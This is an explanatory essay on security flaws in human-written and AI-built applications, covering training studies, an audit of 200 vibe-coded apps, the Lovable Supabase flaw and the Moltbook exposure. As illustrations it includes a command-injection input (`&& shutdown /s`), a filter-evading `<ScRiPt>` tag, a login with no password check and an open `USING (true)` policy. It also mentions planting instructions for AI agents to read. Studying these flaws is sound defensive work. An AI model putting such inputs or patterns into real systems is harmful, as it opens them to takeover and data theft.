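Google could remove Firebase's test mode and start every database locked. That would keep strangers out until the developer wrote a rule, just as MongoDB's default keeps them out until someone opens the database to the network. It would not fix rules that give legitimate users access to each other's data. As with web frameworks, the right rules depend on what the app is for, and applications built with AI have the same problem.

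## Whether experience and training produce safer code

Several of the mistakes described so far came from experienced programmers. GitHub's own developers overlooked a protection in Rails, and apps with more than 100 million downloads had leaking backends. Writing the right access rules takes knowledge, which seems to call for better-trained programmers, but training may help less than hoped if experts leave many of the same holes as novices.

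### Who writes the vulnerable code

Open-source projects keep a record of who wrote each change, so researchers can try to trace a vulnerability to its author. Bosu and colleagues (2014), in *Identifying the characteristics of vulnerable code changes*, analyzed 267,046 code review requests from ten such projects and identified 413 vulnerable changes. More experienced contributors wrote most of them, but a change by a less experienced contributor was 1.8 to 24 times more likely to be vulnerable.

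Both findings can be true because experienced contributors write most of the code. The figures in this example are invented:

| | Core developers | Newcomers |
|---|---|---|
| Changes | 9,000 | 1,000 |
| Vulnerable changes | 45 | 15 |
| Share of all vulnerable changes | 75% | 25% |
| Vulnerable changes per 1,000 | 5 | 15 |

A reviewer who can check only a few changes should start with those from newcomers. But this project would still have three quarters of its vulnerabilities if it had accepted no changes from newcomers.

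The real gap may be smaller than in Bosu's figures, because reviewers may look harder at a stranger's work. The less experienced contributors were also not necessarily novices, since someone who sends a change to a large open-source project can usually program. Another person also reads the change before the project accepts it, whereas the teacher with the school-trips app had no such reviewer.

In *The Secret Life of Software Vulnerabilities*, Iannone, Guadagni and colleagues traced 3,663 vulnerabilities in 1,096 GitHub projects back to the changes that helped introduce them. Newcomers wrote 43% of these changes and experts 40%. To tell whose work was safer, we would also need to know how many harmless changes each group wrote. "Newcomer" here means new to the project, so a programmer with a 20-year career would count as one in her first month.

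The study also found that developers with a high workload wrote 59% of the contributing changes, but this finding has the same problem. Busy developers write more code of every kind, though tired people probably also make more mistakes.

Iannone and colleagues found that more than one change had contributed to the vulnerability in 61% of cases. In those cases, the first and last changes were about four years apart on average. When they checked a sample by hand, however, only 68% of the changes their tracing method had picked out had actually contributed to the vulnerability.

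An experiment gives a more direct comparison because everyone does the same task. Yasemin Acar and colleagues gave 307 GitHub users three security-related programming tasks. *If you want, I can store the encrypted password* (Naiakshina, Danilova and colleagues, 2019) reports that those with more programming experience wrote significantly more secure code that also worked better. Experience therefore seems to help, although people who stay in programming for many years may have been more careful from the start. Across the whole group, though, only 162 of the 307 stored users' login details securely.

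### Traps that experienced developers miss

Oliveira, Lin and colleagues (2018), in *API Blindspots*, tested whether developers notice a hole in code that someone else has written. They recruited 70 professionals and 39 students and told them that the study was about how developers interpret code, without mentioning security. Each participant got six short Java programs, four of which used a function with a known trap. One program was supposed to change the date on a Windows server. In simplified form, it contained this line:

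`run("CMD /C DATE " + date);`

The program passes whatever date it receives to the Windows command line. If someone sends `10-12-2015 && shutdown /s`, the server changes its date and then shuts down. The flaw is like the guestbook's SQL injection, except that the input goes to Windows instead of a database. Participants had to choose the correct statement about the program from five options, and the correct one was that it might do more than change the date.

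Participants' odds of answering correctly were 56% lower for programs with a trap than for those without, yet they were about equally confident in both cases. Their years of programming, technical knowledge and skill in Java did not predict how many traps they spotted. The only personal trait that did was openness, measured by a personality questionnaire.

A beginner might still have done worse, because Oliveira and colleagues compared experienced people with other experienced people. Nearly all the participants had at least a working knowledge of Java, and both the professionals and the students had been programming for about six years on average. The difference between programs with and without traps also came mainly from functions that read and write files. With functions that handle text, like the one in the date program, participants did about equally well with or without a trap.

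In *Blindspots in Python and Java APIs Result in Vulnerable Code*, Brun, Lin and colleagues (2021) repeated the experiment in Python with 129 other developers. The results were similar, though the traps had a stronger effect than in Java. The researchers conclude that experience and education alone do not overcome the problem, and that developers need tools that point out the traps as they write code.

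The latest version, *Software Vulnerabilities as Cognitive Blindspots* (Ivory, Towse and colleagues, 2026), gave eight of the Python puzzles to 37 freelancers. Again, neither programming experience nor security knowledge predicted who would solve them. Some of the freelancers may have had help. On a short reasoning test on which people usually make mistakes, 78% got every question right, compared with 17% in the original study of that test, and ChatGPT could answer nearly all the questions. If participants also gave the puzzles to a chatbot, their own experience would have made little difference. With only 37 people, the study could also have missed a modest effect. Its simulations suggest that Python experience might help a little, but that detecting this would take about 144 participants.

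The freelancers also rated how likely they and the average developer were to introduce five common vulnerabilities. They rated themselves less likely to do so, with an average score of 126 on a scale where 100 means no difference. They can't all be better than average, although successful freelancers might be as a group. A developer who thinks other people make these mistakes has little reason to check for them.

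### Ignorance or carelessness

If programmers' mistakes mostly involve rules they already understand, more teaching won't help much. Votipka, Fulton and colleagues (2020), in *Understanding security mistakes developers make*, looked for the causes of 182 vulnerabilities in 94 programs. Teams wrote the programs for a contest that gave them just under two weeks to build, for example, a secure log or the software that connects a cash machine to its bank. The teams then attacked each other's programs. Participants averaged 8.9 years of experience and knew that security counted.

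Votipka and colleagues attribute at least one flaw in 78% of the programs to a poor understanding of security. Only 21% contained a simple mistake, where the team chose a sound protection but programmed it incorrectly.

Many of these teams knew only the obvious part of a security rule. They encrypted data so that outsiders could not read it, but 23 of the 79 programs that needed a check for tampering lacked one. That might let an attacker change a record without being able to read it. Another 26 programs used a fixed value where they needed an unpredictable one. One team numbered its messages because its encryption method required a different number each time, but the program restarted at 1,337 with every transaction, so it kept using the same number.

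Flaws that come from misunderstanding are harder to find than simple mistakes. Other teams exploited only 71% of them, compared with 97% of the simple mistakes. A novice testing her own program would be even less likely to notice them, since she would have to look for a danger she has never heard of.

Some of the flaws the study counts as missing knowledge look more like forgetting. In one task, teams built a database for several users, with rules about who could do what. Every team wrote some of the nine necessary access checks, but 10 of the 15 left out at least one. Several let ordinary users run commands that should have been restricted to the administrator. These teams evidently knew what an access check was. Their omissions resemble those of the professionals in Finifter and Wagner's study who applied a protection on one page and forgot it on another.

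About three quarters of the teams had come to the contest through a series of online courses that included software security and cryptography, and they still had at least some of their misunderstandings afterward. The courses may have helped anyway, since the same people might have done worse without them. Comparing these teams with the others wouldn't show whether the courses helped, because people chose whether to take them, and those who sign up for a security course probably already care more about security. To separate the effect of the teaching from the effect of this interest, researchers would have to assign programmers to a course at random and then examine code they write when nobody has mentioned security.

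### Passwords, with and without a request

Alena Naiakshina's group randomly assigned people to different instructions, not different training. Across two studies, 40 computer science students wrote the registration page for a university social network. The first study, *Why Do Developers Get Password Storage Wrong?*, had 20 participants. Half the students got a task description that didn't mention security, and half were told to store passwords securely.

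A secure site stores each password in a scrambled form called a hash. When a user logs in, the site scrambles the password they enter and compares the result with the stored hash. The site should also add a random value, called a salt, to each password before scrambling it. Otherwise, two people with the same password get the same hash, and an attacker can look up the hashes of common passwords in a list prepared in advance.

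None of the 20 students who had not been asked for security stored passwords securely, though two tried before giving up and handing in an insecure version. Twelve of the 20 who had been asked achieved at least some security.

Half of each group used Spring, a Java framework with ready-made code for storing passwords. Spring made no difference to students who hadn't been asked to protect the passwords, because they had to decide to use that code. The request made the other students think of protecting the passwords, and Spring then helped them do it well. Among students who achieved some security, all but one of those with Spring scored 6 out of 7, while those without it scored from 2 to 6.

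Of the 28 students whose solutions were insecure, 15 said they would have done better for a real employer. Naiakshina and colleagues therefore pretended to be one. They set up a website for a company that let people share sports photos, said that its developer had just left, and hired 43 freelancers to finish the registration page. Some were offered €100 and others €200. (For the sake of fairness, everyone got €200 in the end.)

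The freelancers did no better than the students. Those who were asked for security were significantly more likely to provide it, but the higher pay had no measurable effect. By accident, the first 17 freelancers got project files that already loaded two of Java's security libraries. This might have alerted those who had not been asked for security that it was wanted, yet none of them stored the passwords securely.

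When a freelancer delivered a program that stored passwords as plain text, the "company" asked for a secure version. Such a request takes a client a minute, but it doesn't ensure that the new version will be secure. One freelancer, hired for a trial run, delivered a program that stored passwords as plain text after 21 hours. When asked for a secure version, he spent another 38 hours on one that encrypted the passwords, so anyone who stole the key along with the database could decrypt them all.

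Some freelancers used Base64, which writes data in a different alphabet. In Base64, the password `secret` becomes `c2VjcmV0`. It looks scrambled, but any programmer can decode it in a second without a key. Sophos News (2019) reports that only 15 of the 43 freelancers used a salt, and that the researchers found 16 cases of code obviously copied from the internet. Every student who produced a secure solution had also copied code, so copying did not always make code insecure.

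The freelancers' descriptions of their own practice were unreliable. Several claimed they would store passwords securely without being told, although their first versions had been insecure. Naiakshina and colleagues also describe an earlier study in which Jason Bau and colleagues compared websites built by start-ups and by freelancers. The freelancers in that study knew far more about password storage than their code showed, so some of them would have passed a written exam at the end of a course.

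### Ten years of awareness campaigns

From the early 2000s, OWASP, SANS and MITRE tried to educate programmers by publishing lists of common security mistakes. In *Have things changed now?*, Scholte, Balzarotti and Kirda (2012) looked for signs that this had worked. They analyzed the CVE catalogue up to 2009 and found about as many reports of SQL injection and cross-site scripting in 2009 as in 2006.

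The number of reports could have stayed steady even as programmers learned to prevent simple attacks, if researchers were finding subtler ones instead. To check, Scholte and colleagues collected published examples of attacks on 2,632 vulnerabilities. They classed an attack as complex if it contained a trick for getting past a filter, such as writing `<ScRiPt>` to fool a program that blocks only `<script>`. Most of the attacks contained no such trick. The simplest ones would have failed against even a basic filter, so many of these programs can't have had one in the vulnerable place.

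Scholte and colleagues conclude that, despite the campaigns, developers either did not know about these flaws or could not prevent them. They call for languages and platforms that make applications secure by design. The counts are consistent with this view, but they don't measure how the campaigns affected the people who read the lists.

The increase in reports up to 2006 came mostly from a growing number of vulnerable applications, each typically with a single report. Many of those applications probably had new authors. If a campaign teaches 10,000 programmers about SQL injection while 20,000 new ones arrive, the number of vulnerable applications can rise even though everyone who took part learned something. Many reports also concerned old code. In the ten open-source applications with the most reports of cross-site scripting, flaws present since the first version were found after an average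 of 4.33 years. A programmer who learned to prevent such flaws in 2006 could still have had an older one reported in 2009.

There was slight evidence that developers of better-known projects learned to avoid SQL injection. Reports of it shifted over time toward obscure applications, which the study defined as those without a Wikipedia article, while reports of cross-site scripting did not. This may be because a program usually queries its database in fewer places than it prints a visitor's text, so developers have fewer places to remember to protect.

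PHP's default against remote file inclusion, which came out during the same period, did not require programmers to learn anything.

### What students are taught

The campaigns also had to make up for gaps in formal education. *A UK Case Study on Cybersecurity Education and Accreditation* (Crick, Davenport and colleagues, 2019) describes a review of the database textbooks used at 44 of the top 50 computer science departments in the United States. Five of the seven books, used at 30 of the 44 universities, did not mention SQL injection.

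The other two weren't entirely reliable. One treated adding escape characters, as PHP's magic quotes did, as equivalent to sending the visitor's text separately. The other printed an unsafe example and explained two pages later that nobody should use it. A student looking for code to copy could easily have copied the unsafe example.

People who teach themselves have similar problems. Crick and colleagues cite a study of the top five Google results for six programming searches, which found SQL injection flaws in six of the 30 tutorials. A novice who carefully works through one of the flawed tutorials will learn the mistake too.

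Accreditation requirements can get universities to teach security. In Britain, the professional body that accredits computing degrees has required them to cover information security since 2010, and at least 61% of courses had compulsory material on it. The US accrediting body did not introduce a comparable requirement until 2019–20, and computer science programs there generally did not require students to take a security course. Crick and colleagues think accreditation plausibly explains the difference. However, they compared only what universities teach, not the code graduates write.

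### Knowing, remembering and being asked

Programmers can learn from a lesson that a password needs a salt, or that encryption alone doesn't prevent tampering. The contest programs suggest that many programmers still lack this kind of knowledge, even after years of experience. An hour's teaching might make a large difference to a novice who has never heard of SQL injection.

Teaching is less suited to the problem of remembering. The developer who misses a trap in a date function is thinking about dates, and the course may have been years ago. A warning can reach her while she is writing the line. In an experiment by Peter Gorski and colleagues with 53 GitHub users, which Naiakshina and colleagues summarize, the programming library itself displayed security advice when someone used it unsafely. Of those who got the warning, 73% improved their code. (The other 27% are a reminder that developers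 can ignore a warning, as Office users did.)

Programmers can also give themselves less to remember. In Votipka and colleagues' contest, teams that kept their security code in one place made significantly fewer simple mistakes than teams that repeated it throughout the program. A course could teach this habit, which would help even when the programmer is tired.

The password experiments suggest training a different group, the clients and managers who commission software. They need to ask for secure storage and have someone check the result, but they don't need to know how a salt works. Many novices have no client, though. The teacher who built the school-trips app was solving her own problem, so there was no one to ask her about passwords. If she has an AI system write the program, she becomes the client, like Naiakshina's invented company, and has to know that passwords need protection before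 she can ask for it.

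## What has been found in applications built with AI

An AI system can write the same guestbook for a professional programmer and for a schoolteacher. The professional can read the code that deletes messages and see whether it checks who is making the request, while the teacher can only test it by clicking the delete button. Both cases are vibe coding in the broad sense of the term, and many figures on the security of AI-written code cover both together.

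### Who reads the code

Jha and colleagues distinguish six levels of autonomy by what a person still approves. At the lowest level, a programmer accepts or rejects every suggested line. At the fifth, the AI plans, writes and tests the program unattended, and the programmer sees only the finished result. The levels describe how someone uses a tool, so one tool can be at different levels for different people. Novices are close to the fifth level even if the tool asks for permission at every step, because approving code they can't read is much like clicking "Enable Content" in Office.

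SecurityWeek's *Vibe-Coded Apps Riddled With Exploitable Security Flaws* cites a figure from the hosting company Hostinger that 90% of developers regularly used at least one AI tool at work in January 2026. *VibeGuard* (2026) reports that the head of Claude Code, Anthropic's programming agent, said in late 2025 that the tool had written all of his contributions to it.

Deng, Fan and Meng note in *Understanding the (In)Security of Vibe-Coded Applications* (2026) that Lovable, whose customers mostly describe their roles as non-technical, reported more than eight million users and over 100,000 new applications a day in early 2026. Many of these applications are probably experiments that only their makers will use.

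Being able to read the code matters for more than security. In *Vibe Coding in Practice*, Waseem, Ahmad and colleagues (2025) describe building a program analysis tool with AI. Within minutes the tool looked ready to demonstrate, but it didn't display its results correctly. Each time they asked the AI to fix this, it added hundreds of lines and the error remained. They finally found the cause, a simple mismatch between two parts of the program, by reading the code themselves, which a novice could not have done.

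### An audit of 200 applications

Deng and colleagues made the most thorough study so far of whole applications built with AI. They searched GitHub for traces left by two tools. Claude Code creates a folder named `.claude`, and Lovable puts its name in the web page. They found 74,800 projects, and 38,078 remained after they removed tutorials and projects that were very small, very large or poorly documented. From these, they kept only projects in which AI had written the first version and at least 90% of both the later changes and the lines of code.

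Of the remaining 9,041 applications, 8,695 were web applications, and 984 of those were online. The median application in the collection had 8,254 lines of code and took just over eight days from the first change to the last. (The longest program by the nine professional teams in Finifter and Wagner's study had 3,686 lines.)

The researchers picked 200 of the 984 at random and had AI agents audit each one four times, once for each combination of two agents and two sets of security instructions. The agents produced 11,150 warnings, many of them about the same flaws. After merging duplicates and removing flaws that a person had introduced, the researchers had 2,125 candidates. Another agent traced whether an attacker's input could reach each flaw and tried a harmless attack on the live site, which left 1,287 candidates. Two of the researchers then examined each of these, and both had to agree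 that an attacker could exploit it.

Researchers confirmed 1,186 vulnerabilities in 182 of 200 applications built with AI, or 91%. Half of the affected applications had six or more. The researchers rated about two thirds of the vulnerabilities high or critical in severity, and 9% low.

| Type of flaw | Number | Share of all flaws | Applications affected |
|---|---|---|---|
| Broken access control | 339 | 28.6% | 64% |
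| Injection, including XSS | 199 | 16.8% | 54% |
| Authentication failures | 176 | 14.8% | 51.5% |
| Cryptographic failures | 112 | 9.4% | 36.5% |
| Security misconfiguration | 108 | 9.1% | 36.5% |
| Five other types | 252 | 21.2% | |

One application, for a healthcare provider, exposed a large amount of customer information because of broken access control. Deng and colleagues also found a command injection flaw that gave an attacker full control of a server.

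Three quarters of the access control flaws were in code that runs on the server, where a user trying out the application can't see them. The high figure for injection is more surprising, since these applications mostly use modern tools such as React, which converts special characters automatically. But an AI system can bypass this protection just as a person can. In one application, the code inserted text from an outside service into the page with `document.write`, a browser command that doesn't convert special characters.

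Larger applications had more vulnerabilities but fewer per line. Those with over 20,000 lines of code averaged 12.4, or 0.22 per thousand lines, while those with up to 5,000 lines averaged 2.1, or 0.85 per thousand. Because an attacker needs only one vulnerability, the lower density would do little to protect users of the larger applications.

The study has no comparison group of human-written applications, so the 91% doesn't show that AI made anything worse. Deng and colleagues print OWASP's figures next to their own but warn against comparing the two directly, because the methods and samples differ so much. OWASP found access control flaws in 3.74% of applications on average, while Deng and colleagues found them in 64%. The nine professional teams from 2007 that Finifter and Wagner studied may be a better comparison, although nine programs are very few. Finifter and Wagner also confirmed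 each flaw, and they found at least four in every program. Most applications built in a hurry seem to have flaws that a careful enough search can find.

It is also unclear how many of the builders were novices. People run Claude Code from a command line, so many of its users can presumably program. The 90% rule shows that AI wrote the code, but not whether anyone read it. All 200 applications had public code on GitHub, so they may differ from applications that people keep private. But the main results were similar for Claude Code and Lovable, which suggests that they don't depend on one tool.

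The use of AI to find the flaws is probably a smaller problem, because people checked every flaw included in the count. The agents could still have missed some, and Claude Code was auditing many programs it had written itself. To test this, two outside security researchers audited 20 of the applications without seeing the results, and found nothing new. The same method also found 95.7% of the known flaws in Juice Shop, a deliberately insecure website that people use for practice.

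### Rules that nobody stated

Deng and colleagues also tried to work out how each vulnerability got into the code. They sorted the causes into three classes, which they call knowledge, objective and memory defects:

| Class | Cause | Flaws |
|---|---|---|
| Knowledge | The request did not mention a necessary security rule | 658 |
| | A security step was left to the user | 72 |
| | The code relied on something that does not exist | 13 |
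| | The instructions themselves were unsafe | 9 |
| Objective | The design was good enough for a demonstration | 174 |
| | A repair of one error weakened a protection | 100 |
| Memory | A protection covered only part of the program | 110 |
| | A temporary solution stayed in place | 50 |

More than half of the flaws (55.5%) come from rules the user didn't state. Someone who asks for a guestbook with a login wants passwords that thieves can't read and a delete button that works only for the owner, but may not think to say so. The application looks the same without these protections. Similarly, none of Naiakshina's students stored passwords securely unless the task asked for it.

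The 55.5% is less certain than the number of flaws, because the researchers worked from the code, its history and its comments. They could identify an unsafe instruction only if someone had saved it in the project. In one such case, someone had instructed the AI to put a secret key for OpenAI's service into the program and hide it with a Caesar cipher, which shifts each letter by a fixed number of places, and the AI did so. Other users may have typed equally unsafe instructions into chats that nobody saved, and the researchers could have counted the resulting flaws under unstated rules.

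One application saved backups of its database in the project folder, and the AI's code relied on the person building it to exclude these files before publishing the project. That person didn't, and the email addresses and scrambled passwords of the application's users went onto GitHub. An experienced developer might well have caught this, but a novice would have had to know that the files existed and that publishing the project would make the whole folder public.

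In 13 cases, a protection relied on something the AI had made up, such as a library function or part of a database. Many such mistakes stop the program from working, so they get fixed during development. One that survived was a call to an encryption function that doesn't exist in the library. Other code caught the error and let the application go on storing secrets without effective encryption.

The objective defects resemble what Android developers did when certificate checks got in their way. One application failed to log users in because of an error from its database service, so the AI added a second login route with a username and password written into the code. Another stored users' access tokens in the browser, "encrypted" with Base64, the encoding that some of Naiakshina's freelancers used for passwords. According to a comment in the code, this was for a demo.

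Among the memory defects, one application got a new check for a secret key, but only on its newest addresses. Eleven older ones continued to accept requests from anyone. Another had a login that, in simplified form, looked like this:

```
app.post('/api/auth/signin', async (req, res) => {
  const user = await getUserByEmail(req.body.email)
  // TODO: Add password verification here
  req.login(user)
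})
```

In one application, the AI left a note in place of the password check because the database had no field for passwords yet. Nobody added the check later, so anyone who knew a user's email address could log in to the live site as that user. The owner's tests would not have revealed the flaw, because the owner would have typed the right password and got in each time. Of the 50 flaws that came from unfinished code like this, 45 were of high or critical severity.

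People make all these mistakes too. For example, most of the database teams in Votipka's contest forgot an access check. But those teams could at least read their own notes, while a novice who never opens the code won't see a comment about the missing password check.

### Row-level security and the Lovable flaw

Applications that Lovable builds often store their data in Supabase, a hosted database that visitors' browsers contact directly, as apps do with Firebase. The browser sends a key that anyone can read in the page, but the key only identifies the project, so the database has to check which rows each visitor may see.

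Supabase uses a feature of the PostgreSQL database called row-level security for this. A rule that lets the guestbook's users read only their own messages could look like this, adapted from an example in Pluto Security's *CVE-2025–48757*:

```
ALTER TABLE messages ENABLE ROW LEVEL SECURITY;

CREATE POLICY "read_own_messages"
ON messages FOR SELECT
USING (user_id = auth.uid());
```

The first line turns on protection for the table, which hides all its rows from ordinary visitors. The rest makes an exception for rows whose `user_id` matches the logged-in user's ID. If the developer leaves out the first line, anyone with the public key can read the whole table. If the last line says `USING (true)`, the protection is on but everyone can still read every row.

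On March 20, 2025, Matt Palmer looked at the requests sent by Linkable, a site built with Lovable that turned LinkedIn profiles into websites. By changing one request, he got the email addresses of about 500 users. In *Statement on CVE-2025-48757*, Palmer (2025) writes that Lovable at first denied there was a problem. Palmer worked at Replit, a competitor of Lovable, so he had an interest in the story, but he published his method and sample data with the names removed.

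Palmer and a colleague, Kody Low, then wrote a program to test the 1,645 projects in Lovable's public showcase. They got the full list because the showcase had the same flaw. The program opened each homepage, recorded its requests to outside services and changed them to retrieve all the data. It found 303 unprotected addresses on 170 sites, or 10.3% of the total sites. The data included names, phone numbers, payment details and the site owners' keys for paid services.

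Some of the 303 addresses may have held only data meant to be public, like the song details in the Firebase study. But the program scanned only homepages and never logged in, so it would have missed any flaw behind a login page. The true share was probably higher than one in ten.

In April an engineer at the software company Palantir found the flaw independently and posted about it, with examples that included people's debts and home addresses. Ten days later Lovable introduced a security scan. According to Palmer, it checked only whether a table had a rule, not whether the rule was correct, so `USING (true)` would have passed. When he returned to Linkable in May, the site enforced its rules for logged-in users but not for requests made without a login. He added a database record that marked him as a paying customer, although he had not paid.

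Palmer published the flaw at the end of May, and it received a CVE number. INCIBE's *CVE-2025-48757* (2025) rates its severity 9.3 out of 10. The CVE catalogue normally leaves out flaws in individual websites, but this entry is for Lovable itself, so the flaw counts once however many sites it affected.

NVD's *CVE-2025-48757 Detail*, the US government's version of the entry, marks the flaw as disputed. Lovable says each customer accepts responsibility for protecting the data in their application. A Rails developer had said much the same about people who build applications in 2012, when even GitHub's programmers had failed to protect theirs. Lovable's customers were much less able to do so, since many had chosen the platform because they couldn't write a database rule.

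### Moltbook

In January 2026 the same omission exposed Moltbook, a briefly famous social network where AI agents posted and people mostly watched. Its founder had announced that he "didn't write a single line of code" for it. *Hacking Moltbook*, from the cloud security company Wiz, describes how its researchers browsed the site like ordinary visitors and within minutes found its Supabase key in the page. As on Lovable's sites, it was normal for the key to be visible, but row-level security was missing.

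Anyone could therefore read roughly 4.75 million records. These included 35,000 email addresses and the secret tokens of 1.5 million agents, which would have let an attacker post as any of them. The database also held private messages from 4,060 conversations, some containing keys for OpenAI's paid service. The agents' owners had treated these messages as private, so a mistake on Moltbook also put their OpenAI accounts at risk.

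Anyone on the internet could also change the data without logging in (Fortune, 2026). Wiz tested this by editing a post. An attacker could have put instructions into posts that thousands of AI agents would read and perhaps follow.

Wiz contacted the founder on the evening of January 31. The timeline shows how hard it was to close the database table by table:

| Time (UTC) | Event |
|---|---|
| 22:06 | Wiz reports the exposed tokens |
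| 23:29 | First fix protects three tables |
| 00:13 | Second fix protects messages and other tables |
| 00:31 | Wiz finds that anyone can still edit posts |
| 00:44 | Third fix blocks editing |
| 00:50 | Wiz finds more exposed tables, with 29,631 email addresses |
| 01:00 | Final fix |

Three hours was quick, and the founder had experts telling him what was still open. A novice without that help might have stopped after the first fix, when the tokens were safe and the site worked. Another researcher, Jameson O'Reilly, had found the hole independently. If two parties found it within days of Moltbook becoming popular, others may have too, but nobody has shown that an attacker used it.

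### AI-written and human-written code

Neither incident shows that a human beginner would have done better. Many of the Firebase apps from 2017 had much the same vulnerability, and people wrote those. Finding out what difference AI makes requires comparing similar code written with and without it.

*Not All Agents Are Equal* (Kraishan, 2026) examined pull requests (proposed changes to a software project) from December 2024 to July 2025. AI agents wrote 33,596 of them and people wrote 4,027. Kraishan searched the new code in 8,933 requests for suspicious patterns, such as a password written into the program. At least one such pattern appeared in 2.9% of the agents' requests and 4.6% of the human ones. Most of the difference came from passwords and keys in the code, and from commands that run text as a program.

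This average covers a wide range across agents, from 1.6% for Cursor to 9.5% for Claude Code. Claude Code's requests were by far the longest, with a median of 495 changed lines against 52 for people, so they had more room for mistakes. The human requests came from 810 projects, while the whole collection covers 2,807, so differences between projects may explain part of the gap between agents and people.

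A search for patterns can't find a missing access check, which was the most common kind of flaw in the audit of 200 applications. Kraishan's projects were also fairly popular, and their maintainers can usually read code and decide what to accept. The result is encouraging for professionals who use AI but has little bearing on the teacher.

Improta, Liguori and Cotroneo (2026), in *What is the Difference Between Me and You?*, tested AI models without a human supervisor. They collected 787,562 functions, or small pieces of programs, from open-source projects and had three families of AI models write code from a written description of each one. A scanner then checked the human and AI versions. The AI code had more security warnings than the human code in Python and Java, and more severe ones. In C, where programmers manage the computer's memory themselves, the human code had more of the severe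 warnings.

The AI's functions were about half as long as the human-written ones. Improta and colleagues think this is because the AI left out code such as error handling and input checks. The comparison is a little unfair to the AI, which was given only a description, while the human programmers knew the rest of the program and had often had years to correct their work. Most of the models were also old by late 2026. The researchers tried a newer one, Claude Opus 4.8, though stronger models have come out since. About a third of its answers to 600 tasks had security warnings, but the rate for ordinary requests should be lower because the researchers chose tasks known to cause trouble.

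*A Large-Scale Comprehensive Measurement of AI-Generated Code in Real-World Repositories* (2026) compares probable AI code in real projects with matched human code, and also finds that the difference in security depends on the programming language. Experiments with programmers are also inconclusive. Jha and colleagues cite one in which people with an AI assistant wrote less secure code and felt more confident about it. Kraishan notes that another such experiment reached a partly conflicting conclusion.

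Many of the best-known figures on AI-written code come without a comparable figure for human-written code. *Securing AI-Generated Code* (2026) cites one study in which 45% of AI-written samples failed security tests, and another in which 12.1% of AI-written Python files on GitHub had a detectable weakness. The rates differ so much partly because the first comes from security tests and the second from files people had published. In *Security Vulnerability Patterns in AI-Generated Code*, Kahn and Hastings (2026) asked ChatGPT, Copilot and Gemini for office automation scripts of the kind non-experts request. They reviewed the scripts with Claude Code and found exploitable flaws in every one. Of the 17 types of flaw found, nine appeared in the work of all three systems, so a novice could hardly have avoided them by choosing a different system.

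Existing code can also affect what the AI writes. *Coding Agents Propagate Vulnerabilities in Code Bases* (2026) reports that agents spread vulnerabilities already present in a code base. An agent reads the project it is working on to match its style, and if the project contains an unsafe query, the agent may copy that too. Android developers spread the empty certificate check in a similar way, but they copied it from Stack Overflow.

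Counts of reported vulnerabilities add little evidence so far. According to *VibeGuard*, researchers at Georgia Tech had traced 74 CVE entries to AI coding tools by March 20, 2026, far fewer than the more than 10,000 vulnerabilities reported in WordPress plugins in 2025 alone. But the count includes only cases where someone recognized that AI wrote the faulty code, which is often impossible, and the CVE catalogue leaves out most of what novices build. *AI Code in the Wild* (2025) attributes over 75% of a sample of vulnerabilities to people. As with the experienced contributors in the section on training, this may only mean that people had written most of the code.

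Security companies' published tests of their own are best read as hints about where to look. SecurityWeek reports that Xint, which sells automated security testing, found 434 flaws in several AI-built applications. The most common were missing limits on how often someone can use a feature, which lets an attacker run up the owner's bill. Authorization flaws came second, and injection flaws were rare. In the audit by Deng and colleagues, by contrast, injection affected more than half of the applications. Xint had AI build its applications for the test, perhaps with newer models than those used for the public applications in the audit, and more than half of the 434 flaws came from a single program.

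The number of flaws reported depends heavily on whether anyone checks the scanner's warnings. Waseem and colleagues ran an AI scanner on seven of their own prototypes, none longer than 6,000 lines, and got 970 warnings. That is at least 23 per thousand lines, over 50 times the density of flaws that Deng and colleagues confirmed. Many of the warnings were probably duplicates or false alarms, though the prototypes may also have been unusually bad.

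### Cheaper attacks on small targets

A website with a serious vulnerability may go unharmed for years if nobody bothers to attack it. The groups that wiped MongoDB databases could attack thousands at once because every open server accepted the same commands. A missing access check is different on every site, so an attacker has to work out what the addresses mean and which data should be private. This was seldom worth the time for a guestbook with 40 users.

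AI can now do much of the work of finding these vulnerabilities. The audit of 200 applications took 128 hours of computing time across all four passes, or less than 40 minutes per application. The agents had the source code, which an attacker often lacks. But Palmer didn't need source code for the Lovable sites. He needed only a program that changed the requests he could see in his browser.

On November 24, 2026, Britain's National Cyber Security Centre (NCSC) reported "a marked rise" since September in cyberattacks assisted by AI (Martin, 2026, *UK cyber agency seeing 'marked rise' in AI-driven attacks*). Attackers were using software that lets AI agents probe a target by themselves. Security testers had originally developed this software to check their clients' defenses. The attackers combined it with cheap open models or illegally resold access to commercial ones. One such program, Artex,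 was reportedly used in an attack on the European Commission in October.

According to the NCSC, these attackers exploited familiar weaknesses and their agents used existing tools, but the agents worked faster than people, searched more thoroughly and cost little to run. The agency says an agent can find in minutes "a forgotten key or an unprotected API" that might once have gone unnoticed for years. (An API is an address through which programs exchange data, like the ones that Palmer tested.) Many of the flaws in applications built with AI fit the agency's description.

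The agency didn't say how many attacks there were or how many of the victims had built their software with AI. *UK faces ‘unprecedented rise’ in cyberattacks in coming months, warns cyber chief* (Martin, 2026) reported that, earlier in November, experts had not yet seen exploitation grow in line with the surge in newly discovered vulnerabilities. Some of the AI-assisted attacks may also have replaced attacks the same people would have made by hand.

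The attacks are noisy for now because an agent that tries everything sends many requests, and the NCSC says good security practice would prevent nearly all of them. That helps a company with someone to watch its servers, but the teacher has no one watching hers. If an agent tries 10,000 addresses on the school-trips app overnight, the only sign she is likely to notice is a larger hosting bill.

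## What reduces vulnerabilities in applications built with AI

A teacher who can't read code needs protection that doesn't depend on her knowing much about security. Researchers have tested whether she can get it by wording her request differently or using a better AI model. The companies that publish these applications and store their data have also added checks and changed settings, but they have released almost no figures on whether this made vulnerabilities rarer.

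### Seventy old mistakes, replayed

Deng and colleagues, who found vulnerabilities in 182 of 200 applications, also tested what might have prevented them. They randomly picked 70 of the vulnerabilities they could reconstruct, spread across seven of their eight types of cause. They returned each project to its state just before the mistake and asked an AI agent to build the same feature again. Then they checked by hand whether the old flaw, or one like it, had come back.

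In the baseline, GPT-5.6 Terra, a mid-range OpenAI model, got a short request of the kind a non-expert might type. Seven other setups each changed one thing. The researchers ran every setup three times for every flaw, which made 1,680 runs in total and 210 per setup:

| Setup | Runs in which the flaw returned | Share |
|---|---|---|
| Baseline | 54 | 25.7% |
| Weaker model (GPT-5.6 Luna) | 83 | 39.5% |
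| Stronger model (GPT-5.6 Sol) | 55 | 26.2% |
| Security instructions added to the tool | 25 | 11.9% |
| Request for production-ready code | 23 | 11.0% |
| Request for well-structured code | 48 | 22.9% |
| Request to review the changes | 50 | 23.8% |
| Detailed technical request | 96 | 45.7% |

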